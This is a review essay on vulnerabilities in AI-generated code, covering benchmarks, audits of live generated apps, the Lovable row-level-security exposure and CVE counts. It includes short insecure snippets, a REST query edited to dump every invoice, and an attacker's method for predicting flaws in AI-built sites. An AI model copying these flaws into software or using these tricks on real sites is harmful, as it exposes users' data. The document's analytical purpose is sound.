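The three-quarters vulnerability rate can't be generalized to all AI-written programs. Every task comes from a place where somebody had already written a vulnerability, and most code, such as a script that renames photographs, offers fewer chances to make a serious mistake. Wu and colleagues also favored hard cases. They ranked the public vulnerabilities by how many files and lines the fix changed and by the size of the project, then chose from the top of the list.

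The scores also can't show whether agents are worse than people. Human programmers got the original code wrong in every task, so they would score zero.

Other features of the test make the agents look better than they are. Each set of security tests checks for one known vulnerability, so a program that passes may still have others. Deng and colleagues ran 560 combinations of vulnerability and agent set-up three times each, and 22% gave secure code on some runs and insecure code on others. One secure result is therefore weak evidence that the next program will be secure, even for the same request.

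Most of the tasks come from public code that a model may have seen in training, and remembering that code can raise or lower the model's score. Wu and colleagues examined 20 failures per model and found that Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6-Sol often reproduced the original code from memory, including the flaw. A model could also remember the published fix.

Newer models write working and secure code more often. In September, Compagna (2026), of the software security company Endor Labs, tested OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra on the company's own set of real-world tasks. The model wrote working code for 82.1% of tasks and secure code for 34.1%, compared with 67.6% and 20.1% for its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic's Claude Fable 5.1 scored slightly higher than Astra, at 87.2% and 36.9%. Endor Labs sells security products, so it benefits if people worry about these results, but it also reports the improvement.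 It leaves some tasks out of the score and uses them to detect agents that recall a fix from memory.

The software around a model also affects its scores. In an earlier round of testing by Endor Labs, GPT-5.5 wrote working code for 87.2% of the tasks in the code editor Cursor and 61.5% in OpenAI's Codex. The shares of tasks with secure code were much closer, at 23.5% in Cursor and 20.1% in Codex.

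### Asking for secure code

The tasks never mention security, so Wu and colleagues reran four of the models with an extra sentence asking for code that was secure and free of plausible vulnerabilities. GPT-5.6-Sol's joint pass rate rose from 24.7% to 46.2%, Qwen3.8-Max's from 22.0% to 37.6% and GLM-5.3's from 21.3% to 38.2%. DeepSeek-V4-Pro's rose only from 18.0% to 19.1%. The share of code that worked changed by at most about three percentage points.

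Three of the models could avoid many of their failures when reminded about security, so those failures came from overlooking it. *Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution* (2026) argues that agents score low partly because nobody states the security requirements, and that agents should be given the ones that apply to each task. That would help a company whose security team can write them, but the bookkeeper does not know which ones apply. A general reminder also did little to improve results in the two weakest categories, server-side request forgery and information exposure, where the agent has to work out what to refuse or withhold.

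Earlier results were less encouraging. Zhao and colleagues found that hints about the vulnerability did not solve the problem on SusVibes. They tested older models, and the agents were adding to existing projects, where earlier programmers had already made many of the decisions that affect security.

Andročec tested a longer request on complete applications. Claude Code wrote six web applications twice, once from a plain specification and once with an added section of general security requirements. Scanners and manual tests confirmed 51 problems in the plain versions and 24 in the versions with security requirements. All 13 problems rated high or critical were in the plain versions. In the most serious one, the program signed its login tokens with a secret written into the source code, so anyone who knew the secret could log in as any user. Only manual testing confirmed that this attack worked.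 The experiment was small, and Claude Code wrote each version only once.

In a follow-up study, *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings*, Andročec (2026) had Claude Code and Codex each build applications from 100 specifications, with and without a fixed paragraph of security requirements, for a total of 400 applications. With the paragraph, scanners reported about a third fewer problems for either agent, down from roughly 20 per application to between 13 and 14. But the number of serious problems rose from 301 to 398.

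The extra problems were in third-party code. The agents met the new requirements partly by installing packages, which roughly doubled the average number of direct dependencies, from about three to more than six. Serious findings in the applications' own code fell from 103 to 54, while serious advisories about dependencies rose from 198 to 344. The agents also added packages the applications didn't need. Among the JavaScript applications whose specifications involved no users or accounts, 95% had a package for logins or sessions when the prompt included the paragraph, compared with 45% without it.

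All of the advisories that came only with newly added packages were traced to three packages: one for storing sessions, one for hashing passwords and one for using a database. The flaws were in tools that these packages use to build themselves during installation. Twelve applications that used only alternatives without such tools had no serious advisories, which suggests that naming suitable packages in the prompt could remove most of the side effect. This evidence is limited, however, because the sample is small and the agents chose the packages themselves.

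This may still be a good exchange for an owner who installs updates, because advisories cover packages but not the application's own code. The larger experiment cannot show whether the paragraph would have prevented the flaw in the invoice page. The paragraph told the agents to let users act only on their own records, but the scanners cannot determine which user owns a record, and Andročec did not test the 400 applications by hand. Most of the improvement was in routine settings, such as security headers and cookie options.

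### Scripts for office work

Few tests cover scripts like the lawyer's. Kahn and Hastings (2026) come closest in *Security Vulnerability Patterns in AI-Generated Code*. They asked ChatGPT, Microsoft Copilot and Google Gemini to write the same three Python programs: one that collects product prices from web pages, one that sends personalised emails to a list of people, and one that watches a folder and sorts new files. Claude Code then reviewed the nine scripts and listed up to five vulnerabilities in each.

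It listed five for each script, 45 in all. These fell into 17 kinds, of which nine appeared in code from all three chatbots and 14 in code from at least two. Kahn and Hastings conclude that the risk depends on the task, not the choice of chatbot.

The overlap is believable, but the counts mean little. The reviewer was asked for no more than five problems per script and found five in every one, so it may have stopped at the limit or padded its list to reach it. Nobody confirmed the findings by hand or attacked the scripts. Some of the 17, such as unused code and the lack of a time limit on web requests, are closer to ordinary defects than to security flaws. The scripts may also be out of date, since the study cites ChatGPT's model as GPT-4o, which is far behind current ones.

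How much the others matter depends on who supplies the input. Kahn and Hastings rate the scraper's failure to check web addresses at 9.3 out of 10, but a user who types in an address could usually open the same page in a browser anyway. The danger is that the scraper also follows "next page" links, so a stranger's page could direct it to a machine inside the company's network. The email script copies names from a spreadsheet into messages, which is risky if the names came from a public sign-up form but harmless if the user typed them. Kahn and Hastings acknowledge that their scores assume bad conditions, and that a script on an isolated computer is much safer.

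### Flaws copied from existing code

When the owner of a private tool keeps extending it, the agent may also repeat mistakes in the existing code, because it reads that code to learn how the program works before adding anything.

In *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases*, Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues (2026) tested in November whether agents repeat flaws found in similar code elsewhere in a project. They took 20 places in real C and C++ projects where a memory flaw had once existed, removed the code and asked agents to write it again. They kept the task the same but prepared two versions of the similar code, one with the necessary safety check and one without. They then ran the finished program on an input known to crash the original.

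All five agents wrote less secure code when the example of similar code was insecure. The average gap was 35.4 percentage points. GPT-5.6 Sol, which had the largest gap, wrote secure code in 91% of attempts after a secure example and 42% after an insecure one. The newer models Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra also copied flaws. The experiment covered only five projects and counted code as working if the project could be built, but the gap is too large and consistent to dismiss.

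In a second experiment, agents wrote 96 new web applications in a folder that held unrelated existing ones. The agents had no need to look at the existing applications, and the effect was much smaller. Compared with an empty folder, insecure existing applications lowered the joint pass rate by an average of 3.4 points, and secure ones raised it by 4.4. Flaws in the existing applications made little difference if they were of a kind that could not occur in the new one.

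Telling agents to follow security best practice helped only partly. With that instruction, GPT-5.6 Sol wrote secure code in every attempt after a good example, but in 68% of attempts after a bad one. Telling agents to match the existing style, a common request in professional projects, widened the gap.

When Sun and colleagues asked three of the agents to review vulnerable code they had just written, the agents identified the exact flaw in 69.9% of cases. Asked separately why they had written the code that way, they cited similar code elsewhere in the project 76.5% of the time. But they rarely volunteered a warning when they finished the job. Claude Opus 5.5 did so for 11.8% of its vulnerable programs and GPT-6 Astra for none. Deng and colleagues found that in about a fifth of the runs that produced a vulnerability, the agent had recognised the risk while working but delivered insecure code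 anyway, often with a comment or recommendation instead of a fix.

So if the bookkeeper later asks for a page of receipts, the agent will probably read the invoice page first and may leave out the same line. Asking the agent to review its work would be an easy precaution, but the researchers asked only about code they knew to be vulnerable, so the experiment did not measure how many false alarms a review would raise.

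### Training agents to plan and test for security

Users would not need to remember any of this if agents considered security without being told. To find out what more secure agents do differently, *SecureVibe* (Wang, Peng and colleagues, 2026) first compared GPT 5.6 Sol with a much smaller model, Qwen 3.5 35B, on SusVibes tasks where both had written working code. The smaller model was less than half as likely to plan for the hidden security risk or to test for it, and it tended to stop once the program worked.

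They then trained the smaller model on four kinds of example. In the first, the agent wrote ordinary features, and in the second, it wrote them after being told which vulnerability to avoid. The third taught the model to list the security requirements that a user's request had left out. The fourth taught it to write tests that a vulnerable program would fail and a secure one would pass.

The researchers then tried two more methods. In the first, the agent attempted tasks and received a reward of 1 for code that passed both sets of tests, 0.5 for code that worked but failed the security tests, and a negative score for code that failed both. In the second, they gave a copy of the model a hint about the vulnerability and trained the agent to choose more like the copy, so that the agent would learn to act as if it had the hint.

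The table gives joint pass rates on tasks that the researchers had kept out of the training:

| Training | New web applications | Features in existing projects |
|---|---|---|
| None | 18.5% | 13.3% |
| Coding examples only | 24.1% | 10.0% |
| Coding, planning and testing examples | 32.2% | 12.7% |
| The same, then rewards | 33.9% | 14.0% |
| The same, then hints | 32.9% | 15.3% |

The training sets in the second and third rows are almost the same size, so the difference in results comes from their content. Wang and colleagues think an agent trained only on finished secure programs learns to imitate how they work without learning what makes them secure.

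The training helped far more with new web applications than with features in existing projects, where the best result was only two points above the untrained model's. The agent has to succeed sometimes to learn from rewards, but only about 15% of its practice attempts on existing projects earned the full reward, half the share on web applications. Hints worked better than rewards on existing projects because the agent could learn from them even when it failed.

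The model also improved on types of weakness that the training had not covered. On 78 such tasks from SusVibes, training with hints raised the joint pass rate from 7.7% to 19.2%. It also raised the share of code that worked from 20.5% to 38.5%, so some of the security gain came from the model writing working code more often. Every trained version also did better than the original model on general programming tasks, so developers would not have to give up ability to get safer code, at least in a model of this size.

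## Audits of generated applications in use

Benchmark tasks come from places where somebody had already made a mistake, so they don't show how often finished programs have flaws. To learn that, researchers need to examine programs that people built for their own purposes and put to use. Deng and colleagues examined 200 generated web applications that were live on the internet and found 1,186 vulnerabilities, with at least one in 182 of the applications (91%).

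### How the audit worked

Generated applications carry no label, so the researchers searched GitHub for traces that agents leave behind, such as Claude Code's settings folder or a line in a web page naming Lovable as the author. They found 74,800 repositories and removed those that were tiny, enormous, barely documented or not applications, which left 38,078. From these, they kept the 9,041 repositories in which an agent had made the first commit, at least 90% of all commits, and written at least 90% of the lines of code.

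The median application had 8,254 lines of code and about eight days between its first and last saved changes. About 96% were web applications. Of these, 984 were live, and the researchers picked 200 of them at random.

Four AI auditors examined each one. Two were versions of Claude Code and two of GitHub Copilot, with different security instructions. The researchers then narrowed down the reports:

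| Step | Reports left |
|---|---|
| Four auditors report possible flaws | 11,150 |
| Researchers merge duplicates and drop flaws that an agent did not introduce | 2,125 |
| An AI agent traces each flaw through the code and tries a harmless attack on the live site | 1,287 |
| Two researchers separately check the code and the site, and both must agree | 1,186 |

False alarms are therefore unlikely to explain much of the result. The auditors probably did not miss much either. Two outside specialists reviewed 20 of the applications without seeing the reports and found nothing new. The auditors also found 95.7% of the known flaws in Juice Shop, a deliberately insecure practice application. That is a weaker test because descriptions of its flaws are widely available online.

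The researchers rated 18% of the vulnerabilities critical and 47% high. Access control was the largest category, with 339 flaws across 64% of the applications. The missing line in the bookkeeper's invoice page is an access control flaw. Injection flaws and flaws in checking a visitor's identity each appeared in just over half of the applications.

Small applications had fewer flaws, but more for their size:

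| Lines of code | Applications | Flaws per application | Flaws per 1,000 lines |
|---|---|---|---|
| Up to 5,000 | 15 | 2.1 | 0.85 |
| 5,000–8,000 | 78 | 4.3 | 0.67 |
| 8,000–20,000 | 83 | 6.3 | 0.53 |
| Over 20,000 | 24 | 12.4 | 0.22 |

One likely reason is that even a small web application needs a login, a database and some way to handle visitors' input, and most of the risk is in those parts. The total number of flaws matters more to an owner than their density, but even two flaws can expose a customer database.

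### Three kinds of cause

Deng and colleagues read the code and history behind each flaw and sorted the causes into three classes. The code below is simplified from their examples.

Memory defects made up 13.5% of the flaws. In these cases the agent had set a security requirement at some point but did not apply it everywhere, or never came back to it. One agent added a check that visitors have a key, but only for its new pages:

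```
app.use("/api/v1", requireKey, newRoutes)    // new pages: key needed
app.post("/transcribe", transcribeAudio)     // one of 11 older pages: no key needed
```

In another application, the agent left itself a note to add password checking later. It never did, so anyone who knew a user's email address could log in as that user.

Objective defects (23.1%) came from putting a working demonstration, or a quick fix for a visible error, ahead of security. One application kept the secret tokens for a user's account on another service in the browser, after "encrypting" them like this:

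```
encrypt(text) { return btoa(text) }    // good enough for a demo
```

The function btoa converts text to Base64, a format that anyone can convert back without a key.

The other 63.4% were knowledge defects, where the user or the agent did not recognise what security required. In most of them, the user had not mentioned a necessary rule and the agent did not supply it. This one cause accounted for 658 flaws, more than half of the total. For example, a page displayed a reply from an outside service without first making it safe:

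```
document.write(JSON.stringify(reply))
```

If the reply contains a script, the visitor's browser runs it, and the script can then act as that visitor on the site.

Sorting defects into these classes is partly guesswork. A reviewer can see from the code that a check is missing, but usually can't tell whether the agent forgot the rule or never considered it. The objective defects are easier to identify because agents often admitted the shortcut in a comment.

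### Changing the prompt, the tools or the model

To see what would have prevented the flaws, the researchers chose 70 of them, restored each project to its state before the flaw was introduced, and asked an agent to build the same feature again. They tried eight set-ups three times each, for a total of 1,680 runs. The standard set-up used GPT-5.6-Terra, a mid-range OpenAI model, and a short request of the kind a non-expert might write.

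| Change to the standard set-up | Runs in which the flaw came back |
|---|---|
| None | 25.7% |
| Weaker model (GPT-5.6-Luna) | 39.5% |
| Stronger model (GPT-5.6-Sol) | 26.2% |
| Reusable security instructions for the agent | 11.9% |
| Request adds that the code should be ready for production | 11.0% |
| Request asks for well-structured code | 22.9% |
| Request asks the agent to review its changes | 23.8% |
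| Request gives detailed technical instructions | 45.7% |

Any user could tell the agent that the code had to be ready for production, and this worked as well as a set of security instructions. Detailed technical instructions made the results much worse. The researchers think the agent followed them literally and used less of its own judgment, so users should be wary of specifying technical details they don't understand. Using the stronger model, asking for good structure and asking for a review made no clear difference compared with the standard set-up.

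The standard set-up avoided the original flaw about three times in four. That may mean newer models are safer than the ones that built these applications, but the original agents might also have avoided many of the flaws on a second try. The researchers looked only for the original flaw, so a run that avoided it could still have introduced other flaws.

No set-up prevented all 70 flaws. Agents sometimes recognised a risk but delivered the insecure code anyway, so Deng and colleagues recommend that the software around an agent stop it from finishing until it has dealt with any risk it has noticed. Owners who don't read the code are unlikely to see a warning left in a comment.

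### The open databases behind Lovable sites

The best-documented exposure is CVE-2025-48757, the weak database rules behind sites built with Lovable. Matt Palmer, who worked at Lovable's competitor Replit, describes it in *Statement on CVE-2025-48757* (2025). In March 2025 he was looking at Linkable, a Lovable site that turned LinkedIn profiles into web pages. He edited one of the requests his browser sent and got the email addresses of about 500 users.

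Many websites keep their database behind a server, which decides what each visitor may see. Lovable's sites let the visitor's browser query the database directly, using a key that anyone could read. Palmer's technical notice, *CVE-2025-48757* (2025), explains that only row-level security then protects the data. If the bookkeeper's site worked this way and had no such rules, a client could change the first of these requests into the second:

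```
/rest/v1/invoices?select=number,total&client_id=eq.17    client 17's invoices
/rest/v1/invoices?select=*                               everybody's invoices
```

Alex Stamos, a former chief security officer of Facebook, said in *The hottest new vibe coding startup may be a sitting duck* (Albergotti, 2025) that getting this design right is possible but extremely unlikely.

The next day, Palmer and his colleague Kody Low wrote a script that tried the same trick on 1,645 sites in Lovable's public showcase. They got the list from the showcase's own database, which had the same flaw. The trick worked on 170 sites, or 10.3%. The exposed data included names, phone numbers, payment details and secret keys for paid services. Attackers could sometimes write to the databases too. In May, Palmer added a record to Linkable that marked him as a paying customer.

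The rate is far below the 91% in the audit because the script tested for one flaw and checked only home pages, without logging in. Palmer's employer stood to gain from the story, but another engineer's findings independently supported it. In April, he posted that he had found home addresses, personal debts and secret keys on several Lovable sites in 47 minutes.

Lovable responded that month with a security scanner. According to Palmer, it checked whether a database had any access rules, not whether the rules were right. He published the flaw on 29 May. According to *CVE-2025-48757* (2025), a record kept by Spain's cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, Lovable disputes the CVE on the grounds that each customer accepts responsibility for protecting their own application's data. Palmer's notice lists no fixed version to install. Each site's owner had to find out that rules were missing and then write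 them.

An application can also have access rules that do the opposite of what was intended. The Next Web's *Lovable left thousands of projects exposed for 48 days* describes an educational application built with Lovable that blocked logged-in users and gave full access to anyone who had not logged in. The error exposed 18,697 user records, including those of students. The researcher who found it reported it to Lovable's support staff, who closed his ticket without replying.

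### Internal tools left open

Generated applications can expose data even when their code has no flaws. The security firm Red Access found 380,000 publicly accessible items made with Lovable, Replit and two similar services while looking for AI tools that its customers' staff used without permission. Axios' *AI vibe-coding apps leak sensitive data* (2026) reports that about 5,000 of them contained sensitive corporate data. Many were private tools that their makers probably never meant to publish. Axios confirmed several of the exposures itself, including a Brazilian bank's internal finances and a British cabinet supplier's conversations with its customers.

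On some of the services, an application was public unless its maker changed a setting, and Google had indexed many of these applications. Replit and Base44, another of the services, replied that a public application is not in itself a security flaw. Base44 added that the owners of two of the applications had made them public on purpose, and that Red Access had withheld the addresses Base44 needed to check the rest. The figure of 5,000 is therefore one firm's estimate, but the cases that Axios confirmed show that a tool written for a few colleagues can appear in search results.

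### Counting CVEs in AI-written code

Georgia Tech SSLab's *Vibe Security Radar*, a running count of public vulnerabilities that AI tools introduced, recorded 78 between May 2025 and 24 March 2026, of which 43 were critical or high severity. The monthly number rose from six in January to 15 in February and at least 35 in March, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Researchers Sound the Alarm on Vulnerabilities in AI-Generated Code*.

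The project starts from published advisories. If an advisory links to a fix, software identifies the earlier change that introduced the faulty lines and checks it for signs of any of 40 AI tools. A language model then judges whether that change caused the vulnerability.

The result is a lower bound. *Agent or Human?* (2026) advises researchers to treat any count based on such marks this way. The project could trace only the 24% of the 46,831 advisories that came with a fix, and the 78 cases are about 0.7% of those. That low share doesn't show that AI-written code is safe. Vulnerabilities often take years to come to light, so most of today's advisories concern code written before agents were common.

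The monthly rise is also hard to interpret, because one popular program under close scrutiny can change the whole trend. In March, five of the ten latest entries on the project's page were for a single program, the AI assistant OpenClaw.

Vulnerabilities in one-off code almost never enter such a count. Vibe Security Radar counts a vulnerability only if it has a public advisory, a public fix and a visible history of changes, so it excludes closed-source code. Nobody issues advisories for programs like the bookkeeper's site, and the Lovable case produced only one CVE for 170 exposed sites. The audit of 200 applications found 15 times as many vulnerabilities as Vibe Security Radar had recorded worldwide in almost 11 months.

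### Comparison with human-written code

None of these findings shows that agents write worse code than people do. Deng and colleagues did not run their auditors on human-written applications, and Palmer did not scan hand-built sites that used the same kind of database. Deng and colleagues do cite figures from OWASP, a non-profit that tracks web security, in which 3.74% of applications had access-control flaws, but they warn against comparing this with their own 64% because the methods are so different. *Securing AI-Generated Code* (Surikov, 2026) cites a study that found a detectable weakness in 12.1% of AI-attributed files on GitHub, but gives no matching figure for human-written files.

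Studies of AI-written code often don't compare it directly with human-written code. *What is the Difference Between Me and You?* (Improta, Liguori and Cotroneo, 2026) lists 12 related studies, and only four of them made that comparison.

The best-matched comparison comes from Mao, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *A Large-Scale Comprehensive Measurement of AI-Generated Code in Real-World Repositories*. They searched GitHub for comments that credited an AI tool with a piece of code, then matched each piece with code of similar length from the same project, written before the project's first known use of AI. A static analysis tool raised 10.0 alerts per thousand lines of AI-written code, compared with 13.6 for the earlier code. The rates of high-risk alerts were nearly equal, at 0.51 and 0.52. The most common alerts in both groups concerned unused code, so the lower total is little evidence that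 the AI-written code was more secure.

*Not All Agents Are Equal* (Kraishan, 2026) compared pull requests from five agents with pull requests from people. Kraishan searched the added lines for patterns that suggest a weakness, such as a password written into the code, and found one in 2.9% of the agents' requests and 4.6% of the people's. Claude Code's rate was 9.5%, but its requests were much longer. The two groups are only loosely matched, because fewer than a third of the agents' requests came from the projects that supplied the human ones. A search for patterns also cannot detect a missing line, so it would not flag the invoice page.

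Improta and colleagues had three AI models write new versions of 787,562 human-written functions from written descriptions. Scanners found more security problems, and more serious ones, in the AI versions in Python and Java. In C, the human versions had more of the serious memory errors. Mao and colleagues found nearly the reverse, with more high-risk alerts for AI-written code in C and fewer in Python and Java. The programming language is therefore unlikely to be the main reason for the differences. Improta and colleagues tested raw output from models that are now old, while Mao and colleagues tested code that developers had chosen to keep.

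How much people contribute may matter more. In the sessions that Baumann and colleagues collected, a scanner found 0.12 new security problems per thousand lines in changes that people wrote themselves, 0.15 in changes that people and agents wrote together, and 0.47 in vibe-coded changes. This comparison comes closest to one-off code, but it is also the least well matched, because the researchers did not compare similar tasks. Vibe coders may build more web applications, for example. The rate across all changes was 0.13, so vibe-coded changes can have supplied only a few percent of the lines. The other two groups may therefore include very large files, such as copied libraries, that make their rates look low.

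The studies suggest that AI-written code is about as secure as human-written code when developers select and edit it, and probably less secure when nobody does. No study has tested that explanation directly. The bookkeeper's realistic alternative may also be an established invoicing service with thousands of customers, rather than a human-written invoice page. None of these studies compares generated applications with such a service.

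### Code that nobody can audit

Every program in these audits was public in some way. The 200 applications had public source code and a live website, Palmer's sites were in a showcase, and Red Access could find internal tools only because they were open. Deng and colleagues also excluded repositories with fewer than 500 lines of code or fewer than ten saved changes, which would rule out the lawyer's script and nearly every other program that runs once.

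Private code could be more or less secure than public code. A script with one user has no access rules to get wrong, and strangers can't send it requests. But people who expect no one to look at their source code may take less care than people who publish it. The 91% figure describes public web applications written mostly by Claude Code or Lovable, and there is no good way to adjust it for a script on a laptop. The companies that run the agents and host the applications can see much of the private code, so they could measure how often it has flaws without publishing any of it.

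## Whether code that nobody else has is harder to attack

Most attackers can't see private code, and neither can auditors. If a flaw exists in only one program, finding it gives an attacker only one victim. Some programmers and security experts therefore think one-off code can be safer than the shared code it replaces, even if it contains more mistakes.

### The case that it is

The best-known advocate of replacing packages with generated code is Andrej Karpathy, a co-founder of OpenAI and former head of AI at Tesla. He posted a warning on the day of the LiteLLM attack, and King of Computer Media's *Karpathy Issues Stern Warning* (2026) reproduces the start of it. According to *Andrej Karpathy Warns of "Software Horror" After Massive Python Supply Chain Attack*, he said that any installation could pull in a poisoned package from deep inside its dependency tree. He suggested using a model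 to "yoink" simple functions, which means having it write code in the programmer's own project that does the same job. A criminal who takes over a package's PyPI account cannot change that code.

Karpathy had tried this himself in February. gu-log's *TL;DR* (2026) describes how an agent gave him about 150 lines of code to replace a library for training AI models using 8-bit numbers. According to gu-log, it worked because the task was self-contained and mostly involved multiplying matrices and converting number types. Extracting a package that is closely tied to a larger framework would be much harder.

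*litellm Supply Chain Attack* reports that Karpathy prefers generated code only when the function is "simple enough" and replacing the package is possible. Rhodes, in *PyPI supply chain attack via litellm and the dependency risk problem*, adds that some packages are too complex, too fundamental or too well audited to replace. Rhodes would keep numpy, the standard Python library for numerical work, but would hesitate to use a fast-changing package from a small team.

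The advice deals with malicious code that arrives through a package, but not with mistakes in the code that the model writes instead. The software blog zwischenzugs argues for importing less because every dependency brings years of updates and security notices. It concedes, however, that custom code is often unreviewed and "full of boring vulnerabilities".

Some accounts of Karpathy's advice add that the programmer can inspect the generated code directly, but by October he said that he no longer read or wrote code (Karpathy, 2026). *HackerTube*, the piece in which he said this, describes a public website of the same name that recommends videos, which Claude built, deployed and secured in about two hours. The site has no user accounts and keeps each visitor's preferences in their own browser. An intruder would find little to steal there, which probably protects visitors better than the uniqueness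 of the code does.

Schneier's argument in *Cybersecurity in the Age of Instant Software* also applies to accidental flaws. Attackers usually have no copy of a program that someone generated for one person or company, so they can't search it for weaknesses. If the owner soon deletes the program, any flaw disappears with it. Variety also makes attackers do more work for each target, because they can't reuse a flaw in a one-off program against many targets as they can with a flaw in a popular product.

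Schneier gives several reasons for caution. He says much of this software will stay on networks for a long time, and people will upload some of it to shared libraries, where attackers can download it. He also says today's generated programs are generally full of vulnerabilities, and he expects AI to become good at finding flaws in finished products without their source code. That last point matters for websites, because every visitor's browser downloads and runs part of the site's code.

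The third argument is that ready-made exploits don't work on one-off code. Many attacks on small websites use scripts written for one well-known product. A script for WordPress, the most widely used website software, first checks for a folder that WordPress sites normally have and, if it's there, sends a request that exploits a particular flaw. The bookkeeper's site returns "page not found", so the script moves on to the next address. Not having the flaw is better protection than hiding a vulnerable page at an unusual address, because an attacker who searches long enough will find the hidden page.

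One-off code still contains other people's code. The React exploit of December 2025 would have worked on any generated site that used the affected features, regardless of who wrote the rest. Attackers can also use tools that require no knowledge of the product, such as sqlmap, which tries to insert database commands through whatever web addresses and forms it is given. Source code can leak too, through a forgotten backup file, a badly configured server that exposes the project's history, or an error page that prints part of the program.

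### What an attack costs

An example with invented numbers shows how uniqueness protects a site. Suppose 10,000 small businesses each have a website, and breaking into one is worth $50 to an attacker.

In the first scenario, all the sites run the same software. Finding a flaw and writing an exploit costs $20,000, trying the exploit costs 10 cents per site, and 60% of the owners have not installed the fix. In the second, every site has its own program, and 30% of the programs have a serious flaw. The attacker must examine each program separately, which takes an expert five hours at $100 an hour. In the third, an AI agent does the same work for $5 per program.

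| | Identical sites | Different sites, by hand | Different sites, with AI |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cost of finding flaws | $20,000 once | $500 per site | $5 per site |
| Total cost | $21,000 | $5,000,000 | $50,000 |
| Successful break-ins | 6,000 | 3,000 | 3,000 |
| Value to the attacker | $300,000 | $150,000 | $150,000 |
| Profit | $279,000 | −$4,850,000 | $100,000 |

Attacking a one-off site pays when

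```
cost of examining the site < chance of a flaw × value of a break-in
```

In this example the right-hand side is 0.3 × $50, or $15. If examining a site cost $500, an attacker would leave all 10,000 alone and examine only other sites where a break-in was worth more than about $1,700. If it cost $5, attacking all 10,000 would make sense.

AI also makes it cheaper to attack identical sites. If finding the shared flaw cost $200 instead of $20,000, the profit would rise to $298,800, so the identical sites would still be the better target. But an attacker who can profit from both identical and one-off sites has no reason to attack only one kind.

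The result also depends on how quickly owners install fixes. If 95% of the identical sites had the fix before the attack, only 500 would still be vulnerable, and even with AI the attacker would make just $23,800. The 10,000 different sites would then be more profitable to attack, because nobody sends their owners a fix.

### Predicting hidden flaws from visible features

If a model tends to repeat its mistakes, an attacker can practise on its code beforehand instead of starting from nothing at every new site, as in the example. Kordonsky, Levi and colleagues (2026) tested this with what they call a Feature-Security Table, which lists the flaws that a particular model tends to introduce with each visible feature of a web application.

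The attacker first asks the model to build practice applications and scans their source code for flaws. Software then uses clues like the names of nearby functions to build a table linking each flaw to one of 59 features, such as logging in, searching or uploading a file. The attacker then visits the victim's site, notes its features and looks them up in the table. For Claude 4.5 Opus, saving a record suggested SQL injection, in which a visitor's input runs as a database command. Downloading a file suggested a flaw that lets visitors reach files outside the intended folder.

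A flaw that turns up everywhere says little about any one feature, so the table ranks flaws by an association score:

```
score = log( P(flaw | feature) / P(flaw) ) − log(1 + 0.8 × U)
```

P(flaw | feature) is the flaw's share of all findings linked to that feature, and P(flaw) is its share of findings overall. U is the number of times the flaw has already been chosen for other features. Suppose 40% of the findings linked to logins concern predictable random numbers, compared with 5% of all findings. The ratio is 8, and its natural logarithm is about 2.08. If the flaw has already been chosen for one other feature, the penalty is log 1.8, or 0.59, and the score falls to 1.49. The researchers also adjusted the shares slightly to steady the scores of rare flaws, and ignored any pairing of flaw and feature they had seen fewer than three times.

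The study covered 1,050 programs generated by six models. Of these, 900 were web applications in five domains: online shops, internal tools, social media, blogs and dashboards. The other 150 were smaller programs from a second benchmark. In each domain, every model received five requests, each in five wordings, and the programs it wrote went into the table. Programs from five new requests per domain were then used to test the table. The list of flaws in each program came from two static analysis tools, CodeQL and Semgrep.

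A prediction counted as a success if at least one predicted type of flaw matched one that the scanner had found in the program. These are the success rates with CodeQL, averaged over the five domains:

| Model | Table includes the target's domain | Table leaves out the target's domain |
|---|---|---|
| Claude 4.5 Opus | 85.0% | 78.9% |
| GPT-5.2 | 84.0% | 80.9% |
| Composer | 78.3% | 75.1% |
| Grok | 76.7% | 75.0% |
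| Gemini 3 Pro | 76.0% | 71.3% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 60.0% | 57.1% |

With all the models' test programs pooled, the table succeeded 69.4% of the time with CodeQL and 72.5% with Semgrep, compared with 10.1% and 20.3% for random lists of the same length.

One match is a low bar, though, because the attacker received an average of about five predictions per program with CodeQL and eight with Semgrep. Precision, the share of predictions that matched a finding, was 54.4% for Gemini 3 Pro and at most 36.2% for the other models. Some of the findings were also false alarms. When a person checked a sample, 82% of CodeQL's findings and 74% of Semgrep's were genuine.

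Many of the predicted flaws would not be enough on their own to let an attacker in. In the table for Claude 4.5 Opus, 15 of the 22 features pointed to a missing limit on how many requests a visitor can send. Without that limit, passwords are easier to guess, but the attacker still has to guess one. The method also predicts flaws other than these common ones. After the researchers removed the three types of flaw that Semgrep reported most often, the method succeeded 63.6% of the time, compared with 18.3% for random lists.

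The 100% success rates in some domains mean little because there were at most five test programs per model and domain. The rates also seem to leave out programs in which the scanner found nothing, because a rate such as 66.67% is impossible with five programs. If so, an attacker who picked sites at random would succeed less often.

### Habits of the model

The table lost only a few points when the researchers left out the target's domain, so a table built from blogs and shops also works on internal tools. Kordonsky and colleagues make the stronger claim that flaws carry over between domains more reliably than they recur within one. On average, 54% of the pairings of a feature and a flaw in one domain also appeared in another, while 36% appeared more than once in the same domain. This comparison is unfair because the four other domains together had four times as many programs, which gave a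 pairing many more chances to reappear.

Individual programs are less predictable than these figures suggest. When Kordonsky and colleagues gave each model the same task in five wordings, the share of pairings that appeared in more than one of the five programs ranged from 12% for Grok to 36% for Composer. The table is useful because it includes only pairings that recur across many programs.

An attacker can predict many of a site's flaws without knowing which model wrote it. When the predictions used another model's table, the share of Semgrep's findings that they included fell by 16.4 percentage points on average, to roughly three-quarters of the original share. Several models therefore have many of the same habits, which fits the similar flaws that Kahn and Hastings found in office scripts from three chatbots.

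The method is cheap. The experiments cost $419.40, including a $200 subscription, or about four cents per site when spread over the 10,000 sites in the example. Success levelled off after about 20 practice applications. Checking whether a predicted flaw is real and usable would cost more, and Kordonsky and colleagues did not measure that across their test programs.

Their method would miss the flaw in the bookkeeper's invoice page, because the scanners cannot detect which invoice belongs to whom. An attacker can find it without a table by changing the number in the page's address, which is one of the first things to try on any site with numbered records.

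The best evidence from real sites is Palmer's scan of Lovable's showcase. The sites had different owners and purposes, but one short script got data from about a tenth of them. Having their own code did not protect those sites, because the weakness was in a database design that Lovable had repeated.

### Repeated secrets and invented packages

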